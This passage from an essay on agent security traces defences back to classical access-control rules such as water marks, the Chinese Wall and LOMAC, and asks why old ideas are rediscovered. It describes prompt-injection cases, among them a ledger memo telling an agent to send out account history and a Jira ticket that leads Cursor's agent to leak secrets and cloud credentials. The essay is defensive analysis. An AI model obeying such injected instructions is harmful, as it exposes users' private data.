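$$i(s) \leftarrow \min(i(s),\, i(o)).$$

A program may write to a file only if the file's integrity level is no higher than the program's own, or $i(o) \le i(s)$. This is called the low-water-mark rule because the program's level records the lowest point it has reached.

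Suppose there are two levels, 1 for trusted and 0 for untrusted. The mail assistant and the user's login script, `.profile`, both start at level 1.

| Step | Result | Assistant's level afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The user asks for a new shortcut, and the assistant adds it to `.profile` | 1 ≤ 1, so the write succeeds | 1 |
| The assistant reads a stranger's email, which is at level 0 | min(1, 0) = 0 | 0 |
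| The email asks for another change to `.profile`, and the assistant attempts it | 1 ≤ 0 is false, so the write fails | 0 |

The second write would also fail if the user had asked for it, since the rule does not consider whose idea the change was.

The rule for secrecy is older. ADEPT-50, the time-sharing system that Weissman described in 1969, recorded the highest classification among the files each job had opened. If $A_f$ is the classification of the latest file and $A_h(e)$ is the record after $e$ files, then

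$$A_h(e) = \max(A_h(e-1),\, A_f).$$

ADEPT-50 also collected the files' compartments, special restrictions such as "CRYPTO". When the job created a new file, the system gave it the recorded classification and all the collected compartments. Weissman called the record a "high-water mark", after the ring that water leaves in a bathtub. He reported that it rarely classified files too low but tended to classify files created late in a job too high. Agents that track labels also tend to label data too restrictively as their prompts grow.

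ADEPT-50's high-water mark only classified new files, so it did not exactly mirror Biba's rule. A job could still write to any existing file that its user's permissions and its own clearance covered. A program with Secret clearance could therefore copy the contents of a Secret file into an existing Unclassified one. David Bell and LaPadula's military model closed this gap by forbidding programs to write to a lower level. Adding that restriction to the high-water mark produces the counterpart of Biba's rule. Reading a secret raises the program's level, and the program may then write only at that level or above. Under this combined rule, an assistant that had opened a tax return could save notes about it in another secret file but could no longer email outsiders.

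### The Chinese Wall

A market analyst who knows one oil company's private plans must not advise its competitor. In 1989, Brewer and Nash, in *The Chinese Wall Security Policy*, turned this rule of the financial industry, which had the force of law in Britain, into a rule for computers. They grouped files by company, $y$, and grouped competing companies into conflict classes, $x$. A user may open a file $o$ only if every file $o'$ that the user has already opened satisfies

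$$y(o') = y(o) \quad\text{or}\quad x(o') \neq x(o).$$

A new analyst can open any file. Once she opens Oil Company A's files, she can no longer open Oil Company B's, though she can still open a bank's. If she had opened Oil Company B's files first, she would have lost access to Oil Company A's instead.

This rule limits what a user may read next, whereas the water-mark rules limit what a program may write after reading. Enforcing the read rule requires a record of who has opened what, and Brewer and Nash argued that the Bell-LaPadula model could not express the policy because it kept no such record. For example, if an analyst falls ill, whether a manager may give her files to a colleague depends on what the colleague has already read.

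Limits on reading alone did not stop information from leaking between competitors. Suppose one analyst has access to Oil Company A and a bank, and another has access to Oil Company B and the same bank. The first could copy A's plans into the bank's files, where the second could read them. Brewer and Nash therefore allowed a user to write to one company's files only if the user could read no other company's data, except data disguised so that nobody could identify the company. Kessler (1992), in *On the Chinese Wall Model*, pointed out that this rule was severe because it let a user write to only one object, and only early in the system's life. He proposed building more walls as the data moved.

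Other researchers extended the idea beyond finance. In *History-based Access Control for Mobile Code*, Edjlali, Acharya and Chaudhary recorded selected requests from each downloaded program and used them to decide which later requests were dangerous. In *Enforceable Security Policies*, Schneider identified exactly which policies a monitor can enforce by watching a program run, and introduced automata for specifying them. An automaton consists of states and the events that lead from one to another. The tax return example needs only two states. Opening the file moves the assistant into the second state, where the monitor refuses all outgoing mail.

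### Cloudflare's Trust Ratchet

The network and security company Cloudflare proposed such a rule in August 2026. In *The Agent Access Model*, Silverlock calls it the Trust Ratchet because an agent's permissions can shrink during a task but never grow. A policy set before the task starts lists the triggering events and the permissions each one removes.

Silverlock's example is an agent that runs every night for a finance team. It fetches a settlement report from a payment processor, compares it with two of the company's ledgers, and posts a short result to the team's message channel.

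1. At the start, the system fixes what the agent may do for the next ten minutes. It may fetch the report, read the two ledgers, use a support operation for certain exceptions, and post to the finance channel.
2. The agent fetches the report, which the policy classifies as protected. The harness, meaning the software that carries out the model's tool calls, withholds the report while the task moves from a "Baseline" state to a "Restricted" one. The agent loses its access to the processor and to the support operation. Only then does the harness give the report to the model, which goes on to read the ledgers.
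3. A memo in one ledger contains an injected instruction to attach the full account history to a support case. The agent tries to do this, and the harness refuses. If the agent tries to connect directly, the network refuses too.

The finance channel stays open, so Silverlock restricts what can go through it. The result may contain only a status and numerical totals, with no free text. Trusted software checks and stores the result, then gives the model an identifier. The model can post the result only by passing that identifier back to the software. Data could still escape if somebody compromised the channel, if the permitted format were too broad, or if the agent found a route that neither the harness nor the network checks.

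Silverlock gives the ratchet's main purpose as limiting data theft, so its closest precedent is the high-water mark combined with a no-write-down rule. The example doesn't use Biba's rule. The agent loses its outside channels because the report is secret, and reading the hostile memo doesn't change its permissions. The memo begins with the words "Reconciliation complete", and a fooled agent might post exactly that status. Biba's rule would have stopped the agent from posting anything to a trusted channel after reading the memo, which would have kept both false and true results from the finance team.

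The ratchet is more flexible than either water mark because its restrictions don't have to follow a ranking of levels. For example, a policy can narrow the agent's access to a database after a particular kind of query. This is closer to the Chinese Wall, since what the agent has already read limits what it can read later.

Silverlock cites none of this earlier work. The oldest of its ten references is a 2014 article on BeyondCorp, Google's method of securing company networks. Silverlock notes that least privilege is as old as access control, but its passages on the ratchet contain no term or example that would point to the earlier work. There is therefore no sign of a link between the two, although an engineer who works on access control could well have come across the idea.

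Silverlock also describes a problem that the ratchet doesn't solve, which is that users with different permissions may share an agent. For example, Alice might be allowed to see revenue data when Bob isn't. Silverlock suggests one possible direction, labelling each item in the agent's context with the authority the agent used to obtain it. In 2025, FIDES already labelled data with who was allowed to read it, but Silverlock's reference list doesn't include FIDES either.

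### From the lethal trifecta to the Rule of Two

Another popular rule has a better documented history. On 16 June 2025, Willison warned that an attacker can steal private data through an agent that has access to it, is exposed to untrusted content and has a way to send data out. He called this combination the "lethal trifecta". One of his examples was a GitHub tool that provided all three by itself. It could read public reports that anyone may file, read private code, and propose changes in public. He advised people who combine tools themselves to avoid the trifecta entirely.

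Eight weeks later, Willison (2025) reported in *Chromium Docs* that Alex Russell had pointed him to a similar rule from 2019. *The Rule Of 2* comes from Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, and concerns programming errors that let an attacker corrupt a computer's memory. Such errors are common in code written in languages like C++, and they are most dangerous when the code handles data from the internet and has extensive permissions. Under the rule, programmers must therefore not combine such a language, internet data and extensive permissions in the same code.

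On 31 October 2025, Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) applied the same form to agents and credited both Chromium and Willison.

| Rule | The three properties | What it requires |
|---|---|---|
| Chromium's Rule of 2 (2019) | Untrustworthy inputs; unsafe implementation language; high privilege | Pick no more than two |
| Lethal trifecta (June 2025) | Access to private data; exposure to untrusted content; ability to communicate externally in a way that could steal data | Avoid combining all three |
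| Agents Rule of Two (October 2025) | A: can process untrustworthy inputs; B: can access sensitive systems or private data; C: can change state or communicate externally | No more than two in a session; otherwise a human or another reliable check must supervise |

The precedent for Willison's trifecta was thus recognized after publication, while Meta credited the source of its rule. That source, Chromium's 2019 rule about memory errors, supplied the form, a choice of two out of three, but no method for withdrawing permissions while a program runs. One of Chromium's remedies also applies to agents. A confined process can convert a complicated image into a plain grid of pixels before a more powerful process handles it, much as Silverlock's agent may pass on only totals and a status.

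Meta widened the third property from sending data to changing anything, so its rule covers sabotage as well as theft. Its relation to the water marks is easiest to see in three cases:

| What the agent does | Low-water mark | High-water mark, no writing down | Agents Rule of Two |
|---|---|---|---|
| Handles only trusted input, reads the tax return, then emails it to an outside accountant | Allowed | Refused | Allowed |
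| Reads a stranger's email, then edits `.profile` | Refused | Allowed | Needs supervision |
| Reads the tax return and a stranger's email, then writes to the stranger | Allowed | Refused | Needs supervision |

Neither water mark blocks all the attacks by itself, and using both would also block the harmless message to the accountant. The Rule of Two allows that message because it is meant to limit the damage from prompt injection, which requires untrusted input. It therefore offers no protection if the model picks the wrong file or accountant by mistake, and Meta says the rule is not sufficient protection against an agent's own errors.

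The rules also differ in timing. A water mark depends on what a program has read so far, so the assistant could write to Maria in the morning and lose that permission only when it opened a stranger's email in the afternoon. The Rule of Two depends on what an agent *can* do during a session, so a developer has to choose in advance which property to give up, for instance by letting the assistant write only to trusted recipients.

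Meta relaxes this in a way that brings its rule close to the high-water mark. An agent may start with A and C, browsing the web, and then make a "one-way switch" to B by disabling communication when it accesses internal systems. The web pages are still in its prompt, so any injected instruction is still active. The switch is therefore safe only if the agent can neither send data nor change anything important afterwards. Meta omits the details of how to do this "for brevity", although builders of water-mark systems had worked on them for years.

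### Self-revocation in LOMAC

Around 2000, Tim Fraser built LOMAC, a module that added Biba's low-water-mark rule to Linux. According to *LOMAC*, a 2001 paper on the module, researchers had been demonstrating strict access controls on Unix systems for 25 years without persuading mainstream developers to adopt them. Developers probably held back because the controls broke existing programs, needed too much administration, or disrupted the way people worked. Biba's rule looked more promising because the system would lower the level automatically, so users wouldn't have to choose one.

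Fraser (2000) explained in a mailing-list post, *LWM (Was RFC: Requirements...)*, that early versions failed on the everyday command `ps auxw | less`. Here `ps` lists the running programs and sends the list through a pipe to `less`, which displays it.

1. Both programs and the pipe start at a high level.
2. `ps` reads some low-level system information and drops to the low level.
3. `ps` tries to write the list to the pipe, which is still at the high level. LOMAC refuses, and `less` shows nothing.

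LOMAC had applied the rule correctly, and no attacker was involved. Secure Systems Lab's *Self-revocation Free Downgrading (SRFD)* uses the term "self-revocation" for when a program loses permissions it still needs because of what it read, and then fails in a way its programmers never prepared for.

Fraser responded by treating all the programs in one job as a single subject. When `ps` read the low-level information, both `ps` and `less` dropped to a lower level. LOMAC stopped checking the pipe between them but made sure that no program outside the job could use that pipe. This worked for commands that people typed but caused trouble with some scheduled jobs, which use pipes differently. Fraser then tried giving the pipes levels of their own.

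SRFD, described in 2014 work from Stony Brook University's Secure Systems Lab, instead makes the failure happen earlier. It tracks the actual movement of data between programs and refuses to open a less trusted file if the resulting drop in trust level would make a program lose access to something it is using. Programmers usually write code to handle a file that won't open, but few expect to lose access to a file that is already open. Because SRFD tracks data instead of relying on job groups, it also works for programs that communicate through sockets, the connections used for networking.

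LOMAC did become fairly unobtrusive. Fraser once reinstalled it on his chief scientist's workstation without telling him, and *LOMAC* reports that the scientist, who was using the machine only lightly, didn't notice for 11 days. But every file in the shared temporary directory had a low level, so a text editor or compiler that needed such files could not run at a high one. An experiment with three levels instead of two protected more of the system, but users had to run separate editors for files at different levels and remember which to use. FreeBSD (2012) documents a version of the policy that still ships with that operating system. It lets an administrator mark a program to start at a lower level and keep the ability to rise again. Letting an agent rise again would be unsafe unless the system also cleared its prompt, because the prompt would still contain the untrusted text.

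### Parallel work and new tasks

An agent can have several helpers working at the same time on different machines, and Cloudflare's design checks them in two places, the harness and the network. If one helper received the protected report before the network switched to the new rules, another could send the contents out in the meantime. LOMAC did not face this danger in the same form.

Silverlock prevents this by withholding the data from the model until every component that enforces the rules has stopped using the task's old state, discarded its stored decisions, and confirmed that it has adopted the new state. The system updates that state in one place, so two simultaneous changes cannot conflict. The harness cancels old work or lets it finish. If any confirmation fails to arrive, the model doesn't get the report. When data arrives as a stream whose secrecy depends on its contents, the harness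 stores all of it until the data has been classified and the switch to the new state is complete.

LOMAC needed little of this because a single kernel compared the levels again at each access. Fraser described this as a way to make correct decisions without a complicated system for revoking permissions. Silverlock extends the earlier designs described here by making the switch across many components and withholding the data until all the components agree.

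Two other parts of the design have close precedents. The restriction applies to the whole task, including every helper, as Fraser's did to every program in a job. The helpers can therefore keep exchanging data, but a protected read by any of them restricts them all. Silverlock's network controls also close or reauthorise connections that the agent opened before the switch. LOMAC had a similar gap, because a program that had mapped a file into memory could keep changing it, unchecked, after losing the right to write. The 2001 paper proposed withdrawing dangerous mappings when a program's level dropped.

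Work that needs a lost permission must restart as a new task. Meta similarly offers a new session with a fresh prompt, but also allows human approval as an alternative. Silverlock doesn't let a person lift the restriction on a running task, partly because people who see too many approval requests stop reading them.

Starting a new task would be a poor solution to the problem Brewer and Nash addressed. They warned against treating each of a user's programs as a separate subject, since an analyst could then read one oil company's files through one program and its competitor's through another, and would remember both. An agent that starts with an empty prompt remembers nothing, so giving it a clean record is reasonable if no text carries over. Silverlock therefore has the system check everything a new task inherits, including stored memories. If the task receives protected data, it starts in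 the restricted state unless someone with authority has approved a lower classification.

Self-revocation still occurs in Silverlock's own example. The support operation exists to handle exceptions, but the agent loses access to it on receiving the report. If the agent then compares the report with the ledgers and finds that a payment is missing, it cannot tell the processor. A new task that included the payment details would start with the same restriction. Silverlock acknowledges that a broad policy will block harmless work, and suggests using the record of refusals to write a better policy for future tasks.

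Stony Brook's approach would help in some cases. The harness holds the report before the agent loses any permissions, so it could first warn the agent which permissions it would lose by reading the report. The agent could then finish its outside work or decline the report. A language model could probably use such a warning better than `ps` could. But no warning would help with the missing payment, because the agent learns about it only by reading the report. To handle that case, the designer would have to keep a narrow channel to the processor open, perhaps one that accepts only a payment number and an amount, as the finance channel accepts only a status and totals.

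## What the cases share and what caused the rediscoveries

One more document helps to show how far the old ideas have travelled. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) advises the people who run security in large companies, and its summary says the underlying concepts "should be familiar to security leaders". Here it is beside the main proposals from the seven cases, with the oldest security work that each one cites:

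| Case | Old result | Modern proposal | Oldest security work cited | Grade | Lost and gained |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Instructions and data | Prepared statements, in use by the 1990s | StruQ, Chen and colleagues, 2024 | Two 2006 papers on SQL and command injection | Borrowed with a citation | Lost the guarantee; gained resistance to simple attacks |
| Instructions and data | Privilege levels in Multics, 1965 | Instruction Hierarchy, Wallace and colleagues, 2024 | A 1965 overview of Multics | Borrowed with a citation | Lost enforcement by the processor; gained a way to follow compatible requests |
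| Confused deputy | Hardy, 1988 | Model Context Protocol's guidance, 2025 | OAuth standards; Hardy only through an encyclopedia article | Borrowed at second hand | Lost capabilities as the remedy; gained a separate token for each server |
| Capabilities | Dennis and Van Horn, 1966 | TACIT, Odersky and colleagues, 2026 | Dennis and Van Horn, 1966 | Borrowed with a citation | Lost narrow tokens by default; gained a check before the program runs |
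| Reference monitor | Anderson, 1972 | Progent, Shi and colleagues, 2025 | Binder, a 2002 policy language | Borrowed at second hand | Lost a policy that people can verify; gained a proof that permissions grow only with approval |
| Information flow | Denning, 1976 | f-secure, Wu and colleagues, 2024; FIDES, Costa and colleagues, 2025 | Denning, 1976, in both; f-secure adds Bell and LaPadula, 1976 | Borrowed with a citation | Lost some useful tasks; gained labels that work around a model |
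| Information flow | Denning, 1976 | Dual LLM pattern, Willison, 2023 | None on information flow | No clear sign of a link | Lost labels on extracted values; gained a simple two-model design |
| Leak through a skipped branch | Fenton, 1974 | CaMeL, 2025 | Denning and Denning, 1977, by Nikolaou and colleagues' account | Labels borrowed; unclear whether the designers knew of the leak | Lost protection for some secrets; gained plans that outside text cannot rewrite |
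| Shrinking permissions | ADEPT-50, 1969; Biba, 1970s | Trust Ratchet, Silverlock, 2026 | BeyondCorp, 2014 | No sign of a link | Lost the rule for untrusted data; gained a coordinated switch across machines |
| Shrinking permissions | Chromium's Rule of 2, 2019 | Lethal trifecta, Willison, June 2025 | Chromium's rule, in a later post | Recognised after publication | Lost Chromium's remedies; gained a warning that users can apply |
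| General principles | Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975 | Enterprise guide, OpenAI, 2026 | STRIDE, a list of threat types from 1999 | Borrowed at second hand | Lost the demand for a small mechanism; gained advice on stopping agents |

Only three of the eleven rows describe rediscoveries: Willison's two posts and Cloudflare's ratchet. Willison's Dual LLM post is a doubtful case, because its word "tainted" may have come from web programming. The other eight rows describe borrowings, three of them second-hand.

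Citing the old work did not reliably protect a design from the old problems. Wu and colleagues cite the right theory and prove that a mathematical model of f-secure is secure. But according to Costa and colleagues, the practical version lets untrusted data affect the agent's plan through implicit flows, the type of leak that Fenton described fifty years earlier.

OpenAI's guide repeats much of the 1975 list without citing it. It tells companies to "constrain authority to the task at hand", which is least privilege. It also recommends independent approval for sensitive actions and records of what each agent did, which are much like separation of privilege and compromise recording. In one of its examples, an invoice agent tries to renew a document-signing subscription that is about to lapse. The vendor and the amount are within the rules, but nobody has authorised the agent to sign a contract.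 The guide therefore recommends that every access request establish on whose behalf the agent is acting and for what purpose. Tymshare's compiler could not express on whose behalf it was acting. But none of the guide's five main principles calls for checking machinery small enough to inspect, which is first on Saltzer and Schroeder's list.

### Different words for the same idea

Someone who does not know the established name for an idea will probably search for the wrong one. For *The Vocabulary Problem in Human-System Communication* (1987), Furnas, Landauer and colleagues collected the words that people spontaneously chose for things in five areas, including text-editing commands and recipes. In every area, the chance that two people favoured the same word was below 20%. They estimated from simulations that a system that recognises only its designer's favourite word will fail 80 to 90% of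 the time in many common situations.

The Trust Ratchet fits this explanation. The older literature calls such rules "low-water mark" and "high-water mark", and a search for "ratchet" or "agent permissions" is unlikely to turn up either term. A search for "capability" has the opposite problem because it returns work on three different subjects.

But the new name could be a result of not knowing the literature as easily as a cause, since an engineer who knew Biba's rule would probably have mentioned water marks. Vocabulary also can't explain the missing citation in Progent. Progent uses the exact phrase "least privilege" without giving a source, though a search for the phrase leads to the 1975 paper within seconds. Furnas and colleagues studied how people name familiar things, and specialists share more vocabulary than cooks or typists do. The 20% figure therefore probably overstates the problem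 within computer security, but it may be more accurate between fields.

### Separate literatures

The information scientist Don Swanson (1986) argued in *Undiscovered Public Knowledge* that a conclusion can go unnoticed because its premises are in papers that nobody reads together. In his best-known example, some papers reported that fish oil makes blood less viscous and blood vessels less reactive. Others reported that people with Raynaud's disease, who lose circulation in their fingers when cold, tend to have viscous blood and over-reactive vessels. The two groups of papers almost never cited each other, and Swanson combined their findings to propose fish oil as a treatment. A controlled trial with 32 patients later found that it helped those whose Raynaud's was not caused by another disease.

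If agent safety and computer security were separated like this, AI researchers would miss the old results and security researchers would cite them. Some of the evidence fits this prediction. The f-secure, FIDES and LLMbda teams all included people who had worked on information flow before, and all three drew directly on the literature of the 1970s and 1980s. LLMbda cites a lot of research on information flow in programming languages, such as *Flow-Limited Authorization* and *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control*. Garby and colleagues could therefore compare CaMeL with earlier systems that had faced the same difficulty.

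The rest of the evidence does not fit this explanation. Silverlock writes about access control for a security company. StruQ appeared at USENIX Security, one of the main conferences in the field, yet the oldest security research it cites is from 2006. Shi and colleagues discuss f-secure, CaMeL and FIDES in their related work section, so they could have found Denning's 1976 paper by following one more citation. The doctors in Swanson's study had no citations to follow between their two groups of papers.

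A more convincing boundary is the one within security, between engineers who manage identities and permissions for companies and researchers who study proofs about information flow. Silverlock's ten references are mostly to access standards, Google's descriptions of its own network and recent papers on agents, and OpenAI's notes are similar. The engineers have their own standards, conferences and vocabulary. They can spend a career without needing a proof about information flow, and the researchers have equally little reason to read about OAuth.

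### Ideas that lost their sources

Under Merton's "obliteration by incorporation", an idea's name stays in use while people stop citing its source. Progent, OpenAI's guide and Cloudflare's model all depend on least privilege, but none cites its source, Saltzer and Schroeder. More oddly, StruQ calls injection attacks a classic concept that "dates back many decades" but supports this with papers from 2006 and 2007. Chen and colleagues evidently knew that the idea was old and saw no need to find out who had it first. That is reasonable, since a 2006 survey of SQL injection is more useful to their readers than a report from 1972.

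This explanation works only for ideas that became common knowledge. Few programmers have heard of Fenton's skipped branch, and Biba's rule never became so familiar in any profession that people stopped crediting him. The better explanation for those results is that they were never widely adopted. Engineers learn most of what they know about security from the systems they use. They learned about permissions from Unix and Windows and about prepared statements from databases, and some learned from Perl to call data "tainted". They did not learn from any widely used system to check a branch that a program didn't take. Strict access controls like those LOMAC added to Linux also stayed out of the mainstream.

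Prior adoption separates the ideas designers borrowed from those they rediscovered or missed better than any of the other explanations. Designers borrowed privilege levels, prepared statements and least privilege, which had been in daily use for decades. Water marks and implicit flows, which they rediscovered or missed, had remained mostly in papers and research systems. The exceptions are capabilities in TACIT and lattices in f-secure and FIDES, where the teams had specialists in programming languages or information flow. With so few cases, this is only a pattern to test on further designs.

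### How old the references are

Research on language models moves fast, and its papers mostly cite recent work. *Forgotten Knowledge* (Singh, Rungta and colleagues, 2023) measured this in about 71,500 papers on natural language processing, the field that produced language models. Around 62% of the works cited were from the five years before publication, and only about 17% were more than ten years old. The median age of cited work rose from 1990 to 2014 and then fell.

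Other fields have also shifted toward citing newer work. *Citation Amnesia* (Wahle, Ruas and colleagues, 2025) compared 20 fields over 43 years, using a dataset of about 240 million papers. Language processing and machine learning had the largest drops in citation age from their peaks, at 12.8% and 5.5%. The growing number of new papers did not seem to be the main reason, because the decline remained after the study controlled for it.

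By the same ten-year measure, older work makes up about a quarter of the references in f-secure, 17% in FIDES, and less than 10% in StruQ and Progent. FIDES is full of classical theory, yet its share of older references is no higher than that of the average paper on language processing. Its seven older references are enough to supply that theory because they include Denning, Goguen and Meseguer, and the 2004 paper on robust declassification that its rule for sending email depends on.

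Recency still seems to matter, though these averages can't show how much. These agents have existed only since about 2022, so anyone who describes the competing defences has to cite recent papers, however well they know the work of the 1970s. A low average reference age may mean that the authors never looked further back, or that they did but also had many new systems to discuss.

### Blogs and company reports

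All three rediscoveries were published as blog posts, the ratchet on Cloudflare's company blog and the other two on Willison's own site. Reviewers for journals and conferences can ask why a paper ignores an earlier result, but a blogger can publish without review. References also serve a different purpose in company writing. Those in OpenAI's guide point security staff to frameworks they can use, and most of Silverlock's identify standards an engineer would need to build the system. Neither list is meant to show where the ideas came from, so the absence of Biba or Weissman from such a list is weaker evidence of ignorance than it would be in an academic paper.

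Peer review doesn't guarantee that a paper will cite older research either. StruQ went through it without gaining any such citations. Bloggers can also correct the record faster. Willison acknowledged Chromium's rule within eight weeks of describing the lethal trifecta, while a conference paper can take longer than that to get its first review.

Researchers can also overlook newer work. Wu and colleagues cite the old theory but not Willison's post, which was closer to their design. Shi and colleagues do cite the post.

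### The same constraints, the same design

Rediscovery may need no special cause. In *Singletons and Multiples in Scientific Discovery* (1961), Merton described 264 discoveries he had studied with Elinor Barber, each made independently by two or more people. Of these, 179 had two discoverers, 51 had three, and two had nine. In about a third of the 264, the discoveries were at least ten years apart. Merton concluded that multiple discovery is the normal pattern in science. He argued that several people tend to reach the same result once the necessary knowledge and tools exist, and that many discoveries look unique only because others who were about to make them stopped when they saw the announcement.

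The ratchet is a good candidate. Suppose a designer has software outside a model that can track what the model reads and what actions it requests, but not how one affects the other. Any secret the model has read might be in its next message. The software can't separate safe messages from unsafe ones by tracing their contents, so it has to restrict where messages may go after the model reads a secret. It can't safely lift that restriction later, because the secret is still in the prompt. These few steps lead to a rule under which permissions only shrink. ADEPT-50's designers had a similar problem in the 1960s, since their system recorded which files a job had opened but not what the job had done with the contents.

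This argument explains how someone could reach the old design without help, but not why so many people tried something else first. Most of the early defences trained the model to ignore injected instructions or filtered its input, and Nasr and colleagues later broke twelve defences, mostly of these two kinds. Anderson's panel could not train a stranger's program to behave, so the checks had to go outside the program. Agent designers could train the model, and for a while that looked easier. Only designers who had given up on training, or had never trusted it, faced the same constraints as Anderson's panel.

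Merton's evidence is also limited because a list of multiples shows that independent discovery happens often, but not how often people faced the same constraints and found nothing. Whether two discoveries count as the same also depends on how much detail one compares. The Trust Ratchet and the high-water mark, for example, match in outline but differ in how a new restriction takes effect across many machines.

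### The dispute over whether this is rediscovery

Christodorescu and colleagues argue most directly that agent security research has neglected earlier work. They say most of the literature on securing agents takes the standpoint of AI research, lacks both the perspective and the guarantees of systems security, and does not use decades of earlier work. Their companion paper, *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, calls efforts to make models more robust "the dominant viewpoint in the community".

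Neither paper counts publications, so "most" and "dominant" are expert impressions. The experts are well placed to judge, though, since Rehberger, a co-author of the first paper, found most of the attacks it analyses, and those attacks worked on real products from OpenAI, Microsoft, Anthropic and others. The position paper adds that AI researchers had a warning from their own field, where attackers had repeatedly got past defences for image classifiers.

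Many of the best-known designs, however, including f-secure, FIDES, TACIT and LLMbda, cite the old work openly and come from people trained in security. By 2026 the comparison with classical security had become common. Narisetty and colleagues sort CaMeL, FIDES, Progent and several other systems under Biba's rules, reference monitors and least privilege, but write that this framing "is not ours to claim" and name three earlier papers that had used it. Christodorescu and colleagues themselves call designs that treat the model as untrusted an "increasingly prominent" line of work.

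Much of the disagreement arises because the two sides have different papers in mind. Christodorescu and colleagues are talking about the whole literature, which includes many papers on training and filtering. The reply is about a small set of systems that enforce rules outside the model. People who build such systems are already thinking like security engineers and are more likely to know the sources. The table at the start of this discussion has the same bias, because its proposals were chosen for their resemblance to old results. Only a count over a random sample of papers on agent security could test whether "most" is accurate.

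Citations are also a poor measure of whether a design has the security perspective. Progent cites almost no old work but is recognisably a reference monitor. RTBAS does not mention Biba by name, but Narisetty and colleagues think it enforces his rule. AgentSandbox cites the 1975 principles yet relies heavily on filters that are themselves language models. Ranking these designs by their references would put them in nearly the wrong order. Progent can fairly be criticised for neglecting earlier scholarship, but AgentSandbox is a better target for complaints about unsafe design.

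Computer security has also forgotten many of its own results. Security researchers rediscovered Fenton's example, and Garby and colleagues arrived at a definition of security that others had already published. Paul Karger and Roger Schell had tested the security of Multics for the US Air Force in the early 1970s. In *Thirty Years Later* (2002), they judged that Multics had been more secure than the systems then in use. The industry had moved to cheaper, more popular computers that lacked much of Multics's protection.

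So AI researchers are only partly to blame for the gap. An AI researcher who looked to ordinary security practice for guidance in 2023 would have found least privilege everywhere and complete mediation in decline. They would have had to ask specialists or read the older literature to learn that a value can lose its label when a program skips a branch.

### Approval prompts, a lesson partly remembered

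Designers of agents do remember from older software that people stop reading approval requests when there are too many of them. Willison predicted this for agents in 2023, and Costa and colleagues warn of "confirmation fatigue". Silverlock writes that Windows User Account Control asked people to confirm so many actions that "the prompt became noise". Neither Silverlock nor Costa and colleagues give figures, although researchers and companies have published quite a few.

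Microsoft introduced User Account Control in Windows Vista, which it released to the public in 2007. When a program tried to make changes that required administrator rights, Windows prompted the user for approval. Ben Fathi (2008), then a Microsoft vice-president, reported the results in *User Account Control*, a post on the company's Engineering Windows 7 blog. Users approved 89% of the prompts in the original version of Vista and 91% after its first major update. In a laboratory study, only 13% of participants could explain in any detail why they were seeing a prompt. Fathi worried that people were answering out of habit.

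Phones had a similar problem. Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012), in *Android Permissions*, surveyed 308 Android users online and observed another 25 in a laboratory. At the time, Android listed the permissions an app requested before the user installed it. In each group, 17% paid attention to the list. Only 3% of the survey respondents correctly answered all three questions about what particular permissions meant. David Wagner, a co-author, later helped design StruQ.

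Users sometimes pay more attention than this. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analyzed more than 25 million security warnings shown in Chrome and Firefox. Firefox users clicked past about a tenth of the warnings about malicious and deceptive sites. Chrome users clicked past 70% of the warnings about a site's security certificate, compared with 33% for Firefox users. The design of a warning evidently affects whether people heed it, and the frequency of false alarms probably does too.

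Anthropic (2026) reports in *Claude Code auto mode* that users of its programming agent, Claude Code, approve 93% of permission requests, close to the Vista figure. *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that new users let the agent approve all its own actions in about 20% of sessions, and experienced users in more than 40%. Experienced users also interrupted the agent in about 9% of its turns, compared with 5% for new users. They may have moved from checking each step in advance to watching the work and stepping in when something looked wrong. This is a reasonable way to catch a bad edit to a program, but it is not much use against an agent that sends a password to a stranger in under a second.

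A 93% approval rate could mean that people are careless, or that 93% of the requests were harmless and users correctly refused the rest. To tell which, researchers would have to mix harmful requests with ordinary ones and count how many people refused the harmful ones. Felt and colleagues came closer to this by watching where people looked and asking what they had understood.

Progent's figures need similar care. Shi and colleagues took the small share of policy updates that needed approval, 6%, as a sign that involving users would add little burden. That share measures how often the system would ask users, but not how well they would answer, which decides whether Progent's guarantee holds. Infrequent requests should help if people save their attention for rare events, but they could also leave people unprepared after a long run of updates that needed no thought. Shi and colleagues list mistaken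 approval among Progent's limitations, and found in a separate test that the system still blocked many attacks when users made such mistakes.

One of the eleven attacks in *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* shows the risk when people tire of approving an agent's actions. An attacker hid instructions in a ticket in Jira, a system programmers use to track work. When the code editor Cursor read the ticket, its agent could leak the project's secrets and even the user's Amazon cloud credentials. The attack worked only if the developer had turned off approval for the Jira connection or had put Cursor into a mode that runs most actions without asking. Software companies offer these settings because constant requests make an agent tedious to use. Saltzer and Schroeder warned about this in their principle of psychological acceptability, since people will get around protection that makes their work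 harder.

Newer designs are meant to reduce the number of approval requests and improve those that remain. Silverlock lets an agent do anything within its task's limits without asking and refuses anything outside them. People approve only the limits and a few high-risk actions. OpenAI recommends showing the reviewer what an action will do, what it will affect and where any data will go, instead of just the name of a familiar service. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites a 2012 proposal, *User-Driven Access Control*, that would eliminate many requests. Under that design, pressing a camera button in an app also gives the app permission to take the picture, so the user never sees a separate prompt. This scheme is harder to apply to agents because people use them to avoid pressing the buttons themselves.

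## How researchers could search earlier work better

Engineers are unlikely to learn about water marks at work, but they can still find them by searching. The search works poorly if they describe the rule in today's words. Cloudflare's Trust Ratchet, for example, shrinks a program's permissions after it reads sensitive data. To find the oldest published rule that does this, an engineer could try searching for the function and leaving out the name.

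### A worked search

The search ended at the 1969 paper on ADEPT-50 by Weissman, with help from a review of the field, *A Survey of Formal Models for Computer Security* (Landwehr, 1981). These were the main queries, in order:

| Query | Where | Results |
|---|---|---|
| permissions shrink after the program reads sensitive data | arXiv, a preprint server | Four papers on permissions for phone, mini-program or cloud apps, none relevant |
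| The same | Web | Twenty pages, nearly all on file-permission settings, none relevant |
| access control subject level changes according to what it has read, plus "mandatory access control", "label" and "clearance" | Web | Mostly manuals from the right field, but not this rule |
| floating label, "high water mark", "low water mark", subject demotion, access control history, ADEPT-50, Weissman, Biba | Web | The 1969 paper, in fourth place, and the 1981 survey |
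| The title and report number of Biba's report | Web | An official copy of the April 1977 revision |
| agent loses tool permissions after reading untrusted or sensitive data | arXiv, from June 2025 | Ten papers on agents; no mention of water marks in the passages returned |

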